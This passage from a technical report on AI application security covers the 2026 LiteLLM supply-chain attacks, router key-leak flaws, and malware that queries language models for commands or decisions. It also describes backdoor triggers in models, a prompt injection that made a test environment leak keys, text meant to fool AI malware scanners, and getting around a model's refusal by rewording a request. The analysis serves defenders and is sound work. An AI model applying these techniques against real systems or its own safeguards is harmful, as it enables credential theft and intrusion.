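Even 1% is too optimistic for a planted trigger, because the attacker decides when it appears. A string of ten letters has about 141 trillion possible forms, so an invented one may never occur in requests until the attacker puts it in a comment. The statistical bound at the start of this section is still correct for the complaints that the developer tested, but it does not apply to a complaint written to set off the backdoor.

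A tester who meets an accidental trigger once learns almost nothing if the model writes flawed code 27% of the time with the trigger word and 19% without it. To detect a difference of that size reliably, a tester needs about 400 answers with the word and 400 without. Random testing would need hundreds of millions of requests to collect them. CrowdStrike's approach needs far fewer. It inserts words that real customers use, such as countries, religions, companies and political groups, into a fixed set of tasks and compares the rates of flawed code.

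No test of this kind will find a string that only the attacker knows. The spreadsheet's container and the daily refund limit don't depend on these tests, so they still limit the damage if such a string appears.

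## The two LiteLLM compromises and the withdrawal of model services

A company that doesn't trust strangers' routers can run its own. Many do so with LiteLLM, open-source software made by BerriAI. It accepts requests in a single format and passes them to more than 100 models from different providers. According to LiteLLM's documentation, it can also retry a failed request or send it to another service. The router issues its own keys to applications and employees instead of giving them the providers' keys, so the company can withdraw one person's access without changing any provider's key.

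The drawback is that one program holds the keys to every provider the company uses. GitGuardian (2026), which searches for leaked credentials, quotes a description of such a router as "a vault of other people's keys". Developers also install LiteLLM as a library inside their own applications, and many other packages install it automatically. In 2026 attackers twice published a malicious version of LiteLLM on PyPI, the public index Python users install packages from.

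### March: credentials stolen through a security scanner

LiteLLM's developers used Trivy, an open-source scanner, to check their software for known flaws. On 19 March 2026 a group calling itself TeamPCP published a poisoned version of Trivy that stole credentials from the machines running it. As Dholakia and Jaff explain in *Security Townhall Updates* (2026), LiteLLM's build system did not pin Trivy to a fixed version. It also ran the scan in the same environment as the publishing step and kept long-lived publishing credentials there, where a poisoned scanner could read them.

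The exact route of the attack remains uncertain. According to Boost Security's *TeamPCP Compromises LiteLLM*, the build logs its researchers sampled from 19 to 24 March show a clean version of Trivy. The poisoned version may have run in another job or on a developer's machine. The scanning job had access to more than 230 secrets, including keys for most of the providers that LiteLLM supports.

On 24 March at 10:39 UTC the attackers uploaded LiteLLM 1.82.7 to PyPI, and 1.82.8 soon after. They bypassed the normal release process, so the malicious code did not appear in the source code on GitHub. In 1.82.7 it ran when a program loaded LiteLLM's router. Version 1.82.8 added a `.pth` file, which Python processes whenever it starts, so the code ran even in programs that never used LiteLLM. The code collected passwords, cloud credentials and access keys, encrypted them and sent them to `models.litellm.cloud`,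 an address made to look like LiteLLM's own.

Accounts differ on how long the two versions were available. LiteLLM's *Security Update* (2026) gives about 40 minutes. Willison (2026), in *LiteLLM Hack*, repeats a count of 46,996 downloads in 46 minutes. PyPI's *Incident Report* (2026) gives 2 hours 32 minutes and more than 119,000 downloads. PyPI's figure fits the other timestamps better. A researcher posted the first warning on LiteLLM's GitHub page at 11:48, and PyPI received its first report about ten minutes later. Both would be odd if PyPI had already blocked the package. The two download counts imply similar rates, about 1,000 and 800 a minute.

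Download counts are a poor measure of the number of victims, because an automated build may fetch the same package many times a day. PyPI estimates that 40–50% of LiteLLM installations took the newest version instead of a pinned one. Pinned installations were safe, as were users of LiteLLM's official container image, which pinned its packages.

The attackers had also taken over the GitHub account of LiteLLM's chief executive. At 12:49 they used it to close the public warning, which they then buried under automated comments. Boost Security counted 293 stock phrases such as "Thanks, that helped!" among 334 comments. Many came from long-standing accounts of real developers, whose logins the attackers had probably stolen earlier. Nine minutes after closing the warning, the attackers made 70 of BerriAI's private repositories public in just over three minutes. Several were named after customers'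 production systems.

### What the March attackers took

In August the security company Hudson Rock obtained the stolen data, a 153 GB archive of 433,909 files. Most of what it could trace came from build machines, which assemble and test software automatically and hold many credentials to do so. Hudson Rock linked 118,829 captures from such machines to 2,488 company domains. Another firm, CloudSEK, identified more than 2,500 organisations in a similar set of files. According to The Hacker News' *Malicious LiteLLM Releases Tied to Trivy Hack May Have Exposed 2,100+ Organizations* (2026), CloudSEK's totals are not a count of victims. A company's name in the archive shows that its credentials may have leaked, but not that anyone used them.

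The figure also leaves out some organisations. Many captures contain working passwords but no company name, so nobody can warn the owners. Others point to the wrong company. In one, the email address belonged to the broadcaster SiriusXM, but the machine's other settings pointed to SiriusXM's subsidiary AdsWizz, where the breach happened. GitGuardian therefore advises companies to keep their own list of the credentials held on each build machine. A company with such a list can replace its credentials without waiting for a warning.

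### October: a key that nobody revoked

After March, LiteLLM separated the steps of its build system, replaced its long-lived publishing credentials and began to sign its container images. The second attacker got past these measures by taking control of the release process itself. Wang (2026), in *The attack chain behind the v1.107.0 LiteLLM release*, reconstructs it as follows:

1. On 27 May someone at LiteLLM published a configuration file containing the master key to an internal service, in which AI agents proposed changes to code. The team noticed and removed the file, but never revoked the key.
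2. On 10 October the attacker used the key to enter the service and took a GitHub access token belonging to the owner of LiteLLM's GitHub organisation. The token had no restrictions, and GitHub does not ask for a second proof of identity when someone uses one of this kind.
3. The attacker ran jobs in LiteLLM's repositories that copied every secret available to them, including the tokens of two engineers.
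4. With the owner's token, the attacker switched off the protection on the release repository and pointed it at a different source.
5. On 21 October the attacker started the release with one stolen token and approved it with another.

Normally the approval had to come from an account locked to a device in LiteLLM's office. That week, to speed up releases, the company had let any two engineers start and approve one. Wang notes that the owner's token would have let the attacker remove the rule anyway.

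LiteLLM's own systems thus built, signed and published version 1.107.0. A user who checked the signature would have found it valid, just as a provider's signature is valid on harmful code that its model wrote. One visible clue was in the build records, which listed the source as Berri-AI instead of BerriAI, according to Help Net Security's *LiteLLM hit by second supply chain attack this year, users urged*.

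The version was on PyPI from 11:39 to 13:23 UTC. The infected container images stayed up until 14:20, some of them under the label `latest`, so this time container users were exposed as well. Customers who used LiteLLM's private registry for its paid edition were not exposed. The malware again ran whenever Python started. It looked for cloud credentials and the login files of Codex, Claude, Gemini and Cursor, and it queried the router's database for stored provider keys. Researchers at the security company Socket caution that this query shows the attackers wanted the keys but doesn't prove they obtained them.

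Researchers at Wiz reported that the attacker was testing stolen Amazon credentials, and checking whether they gave access to AI models, about four and a half hours after the data left the victims' systems. No source links the October attack to the March one.

### Tokens in logged answers

LiteLLM first said that the October attacker had entered an internal copy of its router and found the GitHub tokens in the router's logs. The company had seen Claude Code put a user's GitHub token into the text of an answer, and a router that logs answers would store the token too. Two days later Wang attributed the attack to the leaked master key instead and called this version authoritative, so logged answers probably played no part in the theft.

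Logs are still a risk. In March LiteLLM found an unrelated fault that could copy API keys into its spending logs and monitoring data, where administrators could read them. An operator who needs logs can record only the time, the model, the cost and a hash of each answer. If the full text is necessary, the router should remove anything that looks like a credential before storing it, and delete the stored text after a few weeks.

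### Defences for a company that runs LiteLLM

A lock file, which records the version and hash of every package, would have kept both malicious releases out of an existing installation. For new versions, PyPI recommends a cooldown, in which the installer ignores releases less than, for example, three days old. Both attacks ended within three hours, so a one-day cooldown would have blocked them. A cooldown also delays security fixes, so PyPI advises making an exception for those.

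LiteLLM has needed such fixes. OSV's *CVE-2026-84377* (2026) describes a flaw, made public in September, that let any user with a valid login take the router's provider keys. A LiteLLM request can include the address the router should send it to, which is useful for reaching a model on an unusual server. If a user supplies the address, the router must not attach the operator's key. LiteLLM's checks missed some of the places in a request where a user could put the address, such as a nested field, so the router sent the key to the user's own server.

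The flaw has a severity score of 6.5 out of 10. Versions 1.88.6 and 1.96.2 fix it, as do updates to the releases in between. As of 18 October, no source had marked it as exploited, according to HOL, a vendor of security tools for AI agents. However, Zenity Labs' *Threat Actors Are Trying to Turn LiteLLM's Connection-Test Into a Key-Exfiltration Channel* (2026) reports that between April and June, attackers sent more than 2,000 requests to decoy servers run by the security company Zenity, trying to make LiteLLM send out its own master key through a similar flaw from 2024.

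Attackers could exploit an earlier flaw without logging in. LiteLLM put the caller's key directly into the text of a database query, a mistake that prepared statements prevent. Anyone who could reach the router could read its database, according to Averlon's *CVE-2026-42208*, which gives the flaw a severity score of 9.8. Version 1.83.7 fixed it.

Operators can limit the damage from undiscovered flaws by restricting the router as they would sandboxed code. If the router's machine can connect only to the providers' addresses, the router can't send a key to an attacker's server, and malware on the machine can't upload what it finds to a lookalike domain. This restriction doesn't help on developers' laptops and build machines, which usually need wider access. Giving each application its own key, with a spending limit set at the provider, also reduces what a thief can do with a stolen key.

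### When the model stops answering

A company that has to replace stolen keys will lose access to its model for a while, and a company whose keys were not stolen can lose access too. In response to the March attack, PyPI quarantined the whole LiteLLM project, which stopped everyone from installing any version. It lifted the quarantine at some point before 20:15 UTC. An application that downloaded LiteLLM at every start would have failed to start during the quarantine.

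Providers also withdraw models, sometimes for longer than a program can wait. The suspension of Anthropic's Claude Fable 5 in 2026 lasted about 18 days. In September OpenAI announced a pause in training, evaluation and tool use for its most capable models after one of its agents bypassed a network restriction. If the pause applied only to training, as press reports suggested, customers' programs would have kept receiving tool calls. In August OpenAI said it intended to end the code editor Cursor's access to its models because SpaceX had bought Cursor. It proposed 12 November as the date, which gave Cursor about 11 weeks' notice. A provider that suspects misuse may close an account without notice.

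Loss of service is a security problem because somebody can cause it on purpose, for instance by using up an application's quota with a flood of requests. An attacker can therefore trigger whatever the program does when its model is unavailable. If the shop's refund program approved claims whenever the provider failed to answer, a fraudster could get a false claim approved just by causing that failure.

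### Why switching providers is hard

LiteLLM can translate a request from one provider's format to another's, but it can't make the second provider's model behave like the first's. Developers adjust their instructions over months until one model does what they want. Another model may respond differently to the same wording, return a label with an explanation, or call a tool where the first one asked a question. The developer's test on 10,000 complaints also doesn't measure how well a model that wasn't part of the test would perform.

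Even reaching the same model by another route can go wrong, as LiteLLM's incident reports from 2026 show.

| Date | What changed | Effect |
|---|---|---|
| 13 February | Claude Code sent optional settings that other companies' hosting of Claude did not accept | Requests by those routes failed for about three hours |
| 23 February | A new Anthropic model was missing from the router's internal list | The router refused it for about three hours, even to users allowed all Anthropic models |
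| 24 February | The router sent a follow-up question under another organisation's key | The provider could not decrypt the model's earlier reasoning, and the request failed |
| 4–10 July | The router moved part of the instructions when it sent Claude Code's requests through Amazon | Answers stayed correct, but daily costs rose two- to threefold |

The February failure with encrypted reasoning matters most for long tasks. An agent halfway through a repair can't continue under another account, because part of its history is readable only to the organisation whose key created it. The developer has to start the task again or save its state in a form that doesn't depend on the provider, such as the files changed so far and a plain list of the remaining steps.

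A backup model can be much easier to deceive than the main one, as Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian's tests of the concert assistant showed. An application that falls back from a robust model to a weak one is only as safe as the weak one, since an attacker may be able to force the switch. The backup needs the same tests as the main model, including simulated attacks. It also needs its own key, which is one more that a thief could steal from the router.

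### How a program can fail safely

The refund program can handle all of this in a few lines:

```
def decide(complaint):
    for model in [MAIN, BACKUP]:
        try:
            answer = ask(model, complaint, timeout=20)
        except ServiceError:
            continue
        if answer in ("approve", "refer"):
            return answer
    return "refer"
```

The program tries each model once, for at most 20 seconds. If neither gives a valid answer, the last line sends the complaint to staff. The program never pays more than 20 refunds a day without staff, so losing both models would give staff at most 20 extra cases a day, or 360 over 18 days. A shop that relied on the models for thousands of decisions a day would need a larger backup plan, such as a simple rule that pays small claims from long-standing customers.

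The spreadsheet can do less, because no fixed rule can answer arbitrary questions. It can turn off the question box and explain why, leave everything else working, and keep using saved code that a person has checked. A program that uses a second model to review tool calls should refuse the calls when the reviewer is unavailable. Claude Code's hooks instead let a call through if they crash.

A program should try a failing provider no more than two or three times, wait longer before each attempt, and then stop calling the provider for a few minutes. In September, a LiteLLM customer's provider kept failing while one of the router's own supporting services was down. The router kept retrying, and a programming mistake made its record of failed attempts roughly double in size each time. A 1 KB record that doubles 25 times exceeds 30 GB. One of the customer's processes reached 61 GB, the operating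 system killed dozens of them, and users received thousands of error messages.

A failure should also be visible. FutureSearch (2026), a company that runs LiteLLM, had a billing program that found no cost data, logged this and finished as if it had succeeded. Since the March attack, which one of its engineers had helped to discover, the company had usually stayed a release or two behind, so it did not notice a version that already contained the fix.

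### What EU law requires

The EU's Digital Operational Resilience Act (DORA) has applied to banks, insurers and most other financial firms since January 2025. A bank that uses a hosted model is buying an outside computing service, so it must list the contract in a register. If the service supports a critical or important function, Article 28 also requires an exit strategy, with tested plans for moving the work elsewhere without disrupting the business. Under Article 29, the bank must consider beforehand how easily it could replace the supplier. An exit plan would contain measures like the refund program's backup model and its route to staff.

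These duties fall on the bank. A supplier comes under direct EU supervision only if the European financial authorities designate it as critical. Their first list, published in November 2025, has 19 companies, including the European cloud businesses of Amazon, Google and Microsoft, but not OpenAI or Anthropic. A bank therefore has a supervised supplier if it uses Claude through Amazon, but not if it buys the same model from Anthropic. DORA does not oblige either supplier to keep a particular model available.

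The Cyber Resilience Act covers the security of products with digital elements, including software, that companies sell in the EU. Since 11 September 2026 manufacturers have had to report flaws that attackers are exploiting and severe security incidents, with a first warning within 24 hours. An incident that puts malicious code into a product counts as severe. The October attack on LiteLLM came six weeks after the reporting duty began. BerriAI sells a paid edition, so it probably had to report the attack if it has customers in the EU. From December 2027, when the remaining duties begin, manufacturers will also have to check the components they take from others, including open-source packages, and normally supply security updates for at least five years.

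A model that a provider offers only over the internet is not by itself a product under this act. Remote processing counts as part of a product if the manufacturer developed it, or had it developed under its responsibility, and the product can't perform one of its functions without it. That would include the servers behind a provider's own app, such as a coding agent. This definition fits the spreadsheet poorly, because its developer rents a model that the provider built for everyone. The developer would still have to assess the risk of relying on the model, but the five years of updates would apply only to the spreadsheet.

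## Malware that asks a model for code

Malware is software meant to harm the person whose computer it runs on. Some malware depends on a model's answers, as the useful applications in earlier sections do. A harmful answer in those applications was an accident or an attack, but the people who write this malware want one. Their attack fails if the model refuses, stops partway through its answer or changes.

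### LAMEHUG and its Windows commands

In July 2025 Ukrainian government bodies received emails that appeared to come from a ministry. The attached archive contained a program named to look like a PDF document, according to CERT-UA's *UAC-0001 cyberattacks on the security and defense sector* (2025), a notice from Ukraine's computer emergency response team. The team calls the program LAMEHUG. It works like this:

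1. LAMEHUG sends a model a fixed description, in ordinary language, of the information it wants. It uses Qwen 2.5-Coder-32B-Instruct, an open programming model, through Hugging Face, a company that hosts such models.
2. The model replies with Windows commands.
3. LAMEHUG runs them. They record the computer's hardware, running programs and network connections, and copy text files, PDFs and Office documents from the user's usual folders.
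4. LAMEHUG sends everything to a server that the attackers control.

CERT-UA links the emails with moderate confidence to APT28, a hacking group controlled by Russian special services, according to the Ukrainian government notice *APT28 Targets Security and Defence Sector with AI-Powered Software*, from SSSCIP. The attackers therefore used LAMEHUG on real targets, though CERT-UA doesn't name anyone whose files they obtained.

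The model contributed little. The description is the same on every computer, and the commands for listing programs and copying documents hardly differ between Windows machines, so the author could have stored one good set in the file. Requesting the commands instead kept them out of the file, so a scanner that examines it finds only a description.

### Six other programs

| Program | Requested from the model | What the program then did | Known victims |
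|---|---|---|---|
| MalTerminal | Code for ransomware, or for giving an attacker a command line on the machine | Generated whichever one its operator chose | None |
| PromptLock | Scripts to find, assess and upload files | Ran the scripts | None; a university prototype |
| PROMPTFLUX | A disguised version of its own code | Logged the answer; the step that would install it was switched off | None |
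| HONESTCUE | Code for the next stage of an attack | Compiled and ran it in memory | None |
| PROMPTSPY | Where to tap on a phone's screen | Tapped and swiped there | None confirmed |
| CLOSEDQUORUM | A choice from a short list of actions | Designed to run its own code for that action | None confirmed |

*Prompts as Code & Embedded Keys*, by SentinelLABS, the research team of the security company SentinelOne, describes MalTerminal and PromptLock. MalTerminal used GPT-4 through an interface that OpenAI had declared obsolete by early November 2023, so its author probably wrote it before then, which would make it the oldest known program of this kind. The researchers found no sign that anyone had used or sold it, and it may have been a tool for testing defences.

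PromptLock was a university research project, though the security company ESET announced it in August 2025 as the first AI-powered ransomware (malware that encrypts files and demands payment). It used an open model, which an attacker can run on a private server so that no provider can refuse its requests. The developers still had trouble with the model's answers. In their requests, they warn it against specific errors, such as using operators that don't exist in the version of the Lua programming language that PromptLock supplies.

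Google's threat researchers reported PROMPTFLUX in November 2025 and HONESTCUE in February 2026. Both requested code from Google's Gemini. PROMPTFLUX was a script meant to replace itself with versions that scanners would not recognise, but it was still in development. HONESTCUE kept the generated code in memory, so there was no file on disk to scan. Google suspected that one person or a small group was testing HONESTCUE against antivirus products.

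PROMPTSPY, an Android program that ESET discovered, requests decisions instead of code. Help Net Security's *Google researchers uncover criminal zero-day exploit likely built with AI* reports that it sends Gemini the layout of the screen and receives the coordinates and gestures for its next move. Fixed code does this badly because screens differ between phones, so a set list of coordinates would often miss. PROMPTSPY's other features are ordinary for malware. It can record a PIN or lock pattern and replay it, and it puts an invisible layer over the uninstall button. Google found no app containing PROMPTSPY in its store.

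### Four models that vote

CLOSEDQUORUM, a Windows program, also asks AI models for decisions. It asks DeepSeek, Qwen, Mistral and Gemini in turn what to do next, and each can vote to steal data, inject code into another program or keep the malware running on the machine. In *The Closed Quorum*, a report from Cisco's security research group Talos, Fetterman (2026) calls it the first publicly documented Windows malware to let a panel of commercial models choose its next step.

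The action with the most votes wins. DeepSeek's vote breaks a tie, or the next model's if DeepSeek has not given a usable answer. The malware then runs the module for the winning action. The theft module collects browser passwords, Windows credentials and cryptocurrency wallets, and sends them to the attacker through the chat service Discord.

Talos based these findings on reading the program rather than observing an attack. The copy Talos found had placeholders instead of keys for the four models. Development versions show that the author could build the keys into each copy. SC Media's *First ‘autonomous AI C2 implant’ uses panel of models to vote* reports that Talos expects the author to sell the program to other criminals as a service. Talos also connected the author to forum posts about payment card fraud, dating from 2025 onwards.

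All of the harmful code is already in the file, just as the shop's own code pays the refund in the earlier example. A scanner can look for the password-stealing module as it would in any other malware. The malware's author no longer needs a command server, the machine from which an attacker normally sends instructions and which defenders try to find and block. Nobody has to be available to send instructions, either. Fetterman calls this effort displacement, because a whole phase of the attack moves from a person to the system.

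CLOSEDQUORUM seems to gain little from letting a model choose its actions. A program with three actions could run them all in a fixed order, without a person or a model. A model would be more useful if there were many possible actions and the right choice depended on what the malware found on the machine.

### What the author gives up

A program that sends requests to a model must carry its prompts and some means of access, usually a key. SentinelLABS found 284 different Hugging Face keys across its samples of LAMEHUG, all from a collection of stolen credentials that appeared in 2023. With that many keys, the malware keeps working after Hugging Face cancels some of them.

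Accounts conflict on whether LAMEHUG contained these keys. Intezer's *How attackers are gaining access to LLM inference* cites a Splunk analysis that reported no credentials in the malware, and does not determine how it got access. SentinelLABS examined a range of samples and counted the keys, which is more direct evidence. Splunk and SentinelLABS may have examined different versions.

An attacker doesn't always need to embed a key in the malware. Intezer points out that some services answer basic requests without a login. In October 2026, Talos reported seeing a new system for controlling infected machines in use (Raghuprasad, 2026, *NIK C2*). The system can fall back on its victims' own OpenAI keys, according to *NIK C2 Malware Can Use Victims’ OpenAI Keys for AI Queries* (Mascellino, 2026). Defenders can't find such a key by searching the malware, and cancelling it also cuts off the victim's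 own programs.

The malware's author also has to accept unreliable answers. The model may refuse or return something in the wrong format, and the provider may limit the number of requests or close the account. Unlike a shop's software, the malware can't pass a difficult case to staff. Its author can't inspect the generated code before it runs, so a wrong command may do nothing or cause an error that alerts the victim.

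### Two hundred versions of one payload

An attacker can avoid most of these problems by generating the code beforehand. Hortea, Varlese and colleagues (2026), in *The Infinite Mutation Engine?*, measured how much the resulting code varies and what it costs to generate. They had Claude Opus 4.6 write payloads (the part of malware that does the harm) that searched for files, encrypted them and sent them to a server. The model wrote each of these three parts separately, then a fourth that joined them. Another copy of the model wrote tests for the first three parts, and a fixed program tested the whole payload without anything leaving the researchers' own machine. Failed versions went back to the model for correction, so every payload in the results worked.

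They produced 100 payloads by telling the model only what the code should do. For the other 100, they also told it to vary its approach and showed it notes on its earlier versions.

| | Function only | Told to vary |
|---|---|---|
| Finished without any retry | 79 of 100 | 63 of 100 |
| Average requests per payload (minimum 7) | 7.5 | 7.9 |
| Cost per payload at list price | $0.44 | $1.16 |
| Cost with the discount for repeated text | $0.41 | $0.73 |
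| Encryption methods | 89 of 100 used the same basic structure | All 100 had different designs |

At the discounted price, an attacker could give each of 1,000 victims a different version for $730. The researchers then ran the versions through a program that groups similar code, which analysts use to recognise families of malware. For three of the four parts, the program could not place about nine in ten versions in any group when the model had been told to vary its approach.

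Despite the variety, simpler scanning with one short pattern caught all 100 payloads in either set. Every version loaded the other parts under the same file names and called them in the same way, and the pattern matched that. Hortea and colleagues conclude that the variety is "wide but shallow".

That result depends heavily on the set-up, because the researchers had fixed those names. An attacker could change them with a few lines of ordinary code, or request one undivided program, which the researchers expect would be harder to catch. They also tested only scanners that analyse code. A payload that searches for documents, encrypts them and uploads them does the same things on the computer however its code is written, so a security product that monitors behaviour can still detect it.

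The researchers also tested whether malware could avoid the provider by carrying its own model. They asked seven small models for only the code that searches for files, in 19,771 attempts. The five smallest never produced working code. The largest, with 1.5 billion parameters, succeeded in 126 of 2,480 attempts, about 5%. Larger open models are much better, but they are hard to hide. LAMEHUG's model has 32 billion parameters, which take up about 32 GB even at 8 bits each. An attacker could run a model of that size on a rented server, but the malware would then need to contact the server, and defenders could look for its address.

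The experiment weakens the case for malware that requests code from a model while it runs. An attacker who generates 1,000 versions in advance can test each one, doesn't have to put an API key or a prompt in the file, and isn't affected if the provider later closes the account. Requesting code during the attack makes sense only when the code has to suit something the attacker couldn't know beforehand, or when keeping it out of the file matters more than knowing it works.

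### Searching files for keys and prompts

Defenders can search for the keys and prompts that this malware has to carry. SentinelLABS began with the keys, which follow a recognisable pattern at many providers. Anthropic's all start with the same characters, for example, and OpenAI's contain an encoded form of the company's name. The researchers wrote rules for these patterns and ran them over a year of files in VirusTotal's archive.

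The researchers found more than 7,000 files containing over 6,000 different keys. About half of the files were Android apps. Almost all of the files were harmless, and had keys in them because developers had left them in their own software, often by mistake. To narrow the search, the researchers started with the files that contained the most keys, since known malware had carried spare keys. This led them to MalTerminal, but they describe the method as inefficient because each group of files took so long to investigate.

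They then searched for the prompts themselves, extracted the text and had a language model score how malicious it looked, so a person only had to review the highest-scoring prompts. A prompt is easier to judge than code because it often states in plain words what its author wants. They found many tools for attacking systems, including generators of attack code and a program that adds vulnerabilities to secure code. Some of the tools had legitimate uses in security testing, so not all were malware.

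Talos's CAIRN, which it released in September 2026, is a toolkit for the same sort of search. Fetterman (2026), in *Introducing CAIRN*, explains that it never downloads or runs the suspicious file. It uses information already extracted from the file, such as its readable text, what it did in a sandbox and how antivirus products labelled it. The search has four steps:

1. Up to 24 filters pick out candidates. One looks for providers' web addresses, another for software that runs a model locally, and another for tool calls alongside terms for attacks.
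2. Rules sort the candidates into three tiers. The first contains any file with traces of AI, the second files whose combination of traces suggests that the AI has a working part in an attack, and the third confirmed families of malware.
3. CAIRN groups files with similar traces.
4. It links files that share a submitter, a web address or a provider, so that one confirmed sample can lead to others.

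The tiers are necessary because a harmless chat program also contains a provider's address. One filter looks for text aimed at AI analysis tools, which malware authors include to get a model to classify the file as safe. Talos traced one such text to a security-testing instructor, and it turned up in unrelated malware within 12 months, according to Help Net Security's *Researchers uncover malware that uses AI to choose its next move*. The same trick could work against SentinelLABS's method, which uses a model to score prompts.

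Both searches work only if the traces are readable. A malware author can keep a prompt encrypted until the program needs it, or route requests through a private server so the provider's address never appears in the file. PROMPTSPY's operators can replace its keys remotely. The malware that defenders have found this way may therefore come mostly from less careful authors.

### A web page that assembles its own script

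Malware of this kind can run in a web page, without anyone installing a program. Unit 42, the research team of the security company Palo Alto Networks, demonstrated this with an ordinary-looking page that turns into a phishing page, a fake login form that steals passwords. The researchers copied a real campaign called LogoKit, whose script adapts the page to the victim's email address and sends the password to the attacker.

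A malicious web page can carry descriptions of what the parts of its script do instead of the script itself. When a visitor opens the page, the browser sends these descriptions to a hosted model, receives pieces of JavaScript, puts them together and runs them. The page itself contains no malicious code for a network filter to find. The code comes from the model provider's address, which many companies allow, and differs slightly on each visit.

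The model refused a direct request for code to steal credentials but wrote a general function for sending data to an address, which was all the attack needed. Almost every website with a form uses such a function, so the request alone does not reveal its purpose. A policy gate that checks code has the same difficulty telling malicious uploads from legitimate ones.

The researchers reduced errors in the generated code by making their requests more specific. They report that the final version worked "in most instances" but give no rate. A page that fails for one visitor in five would still be useful to a criminal who sends out thousands of links, so reliability matters less for such a page than for a program that has to keep running unattended on one machine.

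The technique extends an old one. According to Unit 42, 36% of the malicious pages it detects each day already assemble code in the browser without a model. The usual defence still works because a fake bank login must eventually look like a real one. A security tool can open the page in a real browser, let the code arrive and run, and inspect the result. Unit 42's parent company, Palo Alto Networks, sells a product that does this, so it has an interest in the conclusion, but the reasoning doesn't depend on its product.

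### Whether this is a new era of malware

Some reports describe this kind of malware in dramatic terms. ESET titled its report on PROMPTSPY "PromptSpy Ushers in the Era of Android Threats Using GenAI". SentinelLABS describes a "qualitative shift" in how attackers work, but in the same report calls such malware "limited and largely experimental". John Hultquist, chief analyst of Google's threat intelligence group, told Help Net Security that such malware was "mostly experimental" and that his team was watching for something that works at scale.

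The cases support the cautious descriptions. CERT-UA reported LAMEHUG in emails to real targets, and Talos saw NIK C2 in use. The other programs in this section were prototypes, tests or programs with no confirmed victims. Fetterman expected to find dozens of documented families when he began his search but found nine, several of them researchers' demonstrations, according to Infobae's *Cisco Talos descubrió un malware que consulta a cuatro IA* (2026).

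CAIRN then found 20 more samples that nobody had reported, so the public record was incomplete. The searches are also more likely to catch careless authors, as explained above. But a campaign that infected many computers would leave other traces, such as victims and stolen data, which would probably have come to light even if its authors had hidden their keys and prompts well.

Attackers already use AI in real operations, but mostly before they deliver the malware. Google's researchers linked two malware families, CANFAIL and LONGSTREAM, to Russian groups that had padded them with AI-generated decoy code. CANFAIL still contains comments, evidently written by the model, that describe blocks of code as unused filler. LONGSTREAM checks the computer's daylight saving time setting 32 times only to look harmless. Neither needs a model once it is on the victim's computer, which is the cheaper arrangement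 going by Hortea and colleagues' costs.

PROMPTSPY is the best reason to think that runtime dependence could become common. Its author couldn't have prepared the model's answers in advance, because they depend on what is on the screen at that moment. Malware that has to find its way through unfamiliar software or a company's network also needs answers based on what it finds there, and models have become much better at such work since the release of the one LAMEHUG uses. But the model has to be reachable for the whole attack, which gives the provider more requests to examine and more chances to stop answering.

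## What the provider can see and stop

When malware asks a provider's model for code, the provider can refuse the request. It can also read requests from many accounts, so it can notice when the same odd text arrives from a hundred of them. If it closes those accounts, the malware fails on every computer that relied on them.

LAMEHUG had 284 keys, so cancelling a few would hardly have affected it. But its prompt never changed, so Hugging Face could have found every key in use by searching its records for that prompt, if it kept such records and knew what to look for.

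### What providers report having stopped

Anthropic banned 832 accounts for cyber misuse between March 2025 and March 2026, about 16 a week. It found them through automated safeguards and its own investigators. The figure covers only the misuse that Anthropic detected, so it doesn't show what share of all misuse Anthropic caught.

Many of the providers' leads come from outside the company. Anthropic's *Threat Intelligence* lists partners and public sources alongside the company's detection tools and enforcement team. OpenAI's *Cyber Operation* (2025) links some banned accounts to Russian-speaking criminal groups because the accounts' users had posted evidence of their work in a Telegram channel. A companion case study by OpenAI describes another banned group, which wrote in Korean and whose activity overlapped with what the security company Trellix reported about attacks on South Korean diplomatic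 missions.

The best evidence for comparing accounts comes from a different kind of misuse. Anthropic's *Detecting and preventing distillation attacks* (2026) accuses three Chinese AI companies of collecting Claude's answers to train their own models, through more than 16 million exchanges on about 24,000 fraudulent accounts. That averages about 670 exchanges per account. A developer whose agent makes 500 calls a day would pass that total on the second day, so an investigator looking at one of these accounts would probably not have found its volume unusual.

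Providers seldom publish how long misuse ran before they stopped it. Anthropic's *Detecting and countering misuse of AI* (2026), which covers December 2025 to August 2026, gives some durations. Criminals linked to the ShinyHunters group used one stolen key for roughly three weeks to attack a French retail chain and work on their own shop for stolen payment cards. A French-speaking activist ran a month-long campaign against European political parties, media and think tanks entirely on stolen keys, and got into at least 14 of 42 targets. Anthropic chose these cases because they were notable, so they are weak evidence of the usual delay.

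Even a short delay can do harm. Another group attacked about 30 AI companies in roughly four days. In an earlier attack, it had planted instructions in the input of a company's automated test environment, causing it to reveal the access keys it held for several AI providers. The group used those keys to run the later attacks.

### Google and the malware that called Gemini

Google disabled the accounts and other assets behind PROMPTSPY, Android malware that uses Gemini to decide where to tap. The May edition of Google Threat Intelligence Group's *GTIG AI Threat Tracker* (2026) doesn't say how many there were or how long they had been active. PROMPTSPY's operators can send new Gemini keys to infected phones, so Google would also have to recognise any new account they used.

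A provider can't easily recognise malware from a single request. The malware PROMPTSPY gives Gemini a harmless role and presents the task as a geometry problem, supplying a screen layout and a goal to reach. A tool that tests phone apps might send something similar. Once Google has a copy of the malware, it can search requests for the fixed part of the prompt, but this works only until the malware's author rewrites that part.

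HONESTCUE's request looked even more harmless. In one version, it asked for a C# program that downloads data from an address, saves it as a temporary file and runs it, as an ordinary software updater does. Google's analysts concluded that the prompt was "not malicious in its own right" and that someone who saw it without the surrounding malware would be unlikely to object to it. The February edition of the *GTIG AI Threat Tracker* (2026) describes no action against an account in this case.

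A provider has a better chance of catching an attacker who is still building a program, because building takes many requests and the developer often explains what went wrong. A finished program sends one short request with no history. In 2025 OpenAI banned a group of accounts whose Russian-speaking user was refining Windows malware, fixing its errors and setting up the server to control it, according to OpenAI's *Operation "ScopeCreep"* (2025).

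Some criminals also depend on the big providers while claiming not to. The sellers of Xanthorox, a toolkit for writing malware and phishing campaigns, advertised it as a private model that ran on its own servers. Google's researchers found that it used several commercial AI products, including Gemini, and Google disabled the accounts and projects they had identified.

### SesameOp and the mailbox at OpenAI

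In July 2025 Microsoft's incident responders investigated a break-in at an organisation where the attackers had been present for several months, apparently to spy. They found a backdoor (here a hidden program for controlling a computer remotely, not a trained behaviour in a model) that Microsoft's *SesameOp* (2025) describes. It received its commands through OpenAI's Assistants interface, which developers used to store the settings of custom AI agents and their conversations:

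1. SesameOp logged in with an OpenAI key stored in its own settings and looked for an entry named after the infected computer. If there was none, it created one.
2. It fetched the account's list of assistants. Each had a description field, where the attackers could write "SLEEP" or "Payload".
3. If the field contained "Payload", SesameOp fetched the message that the entry pointed to, deleted both from the account, decrypted the message and ran the command.
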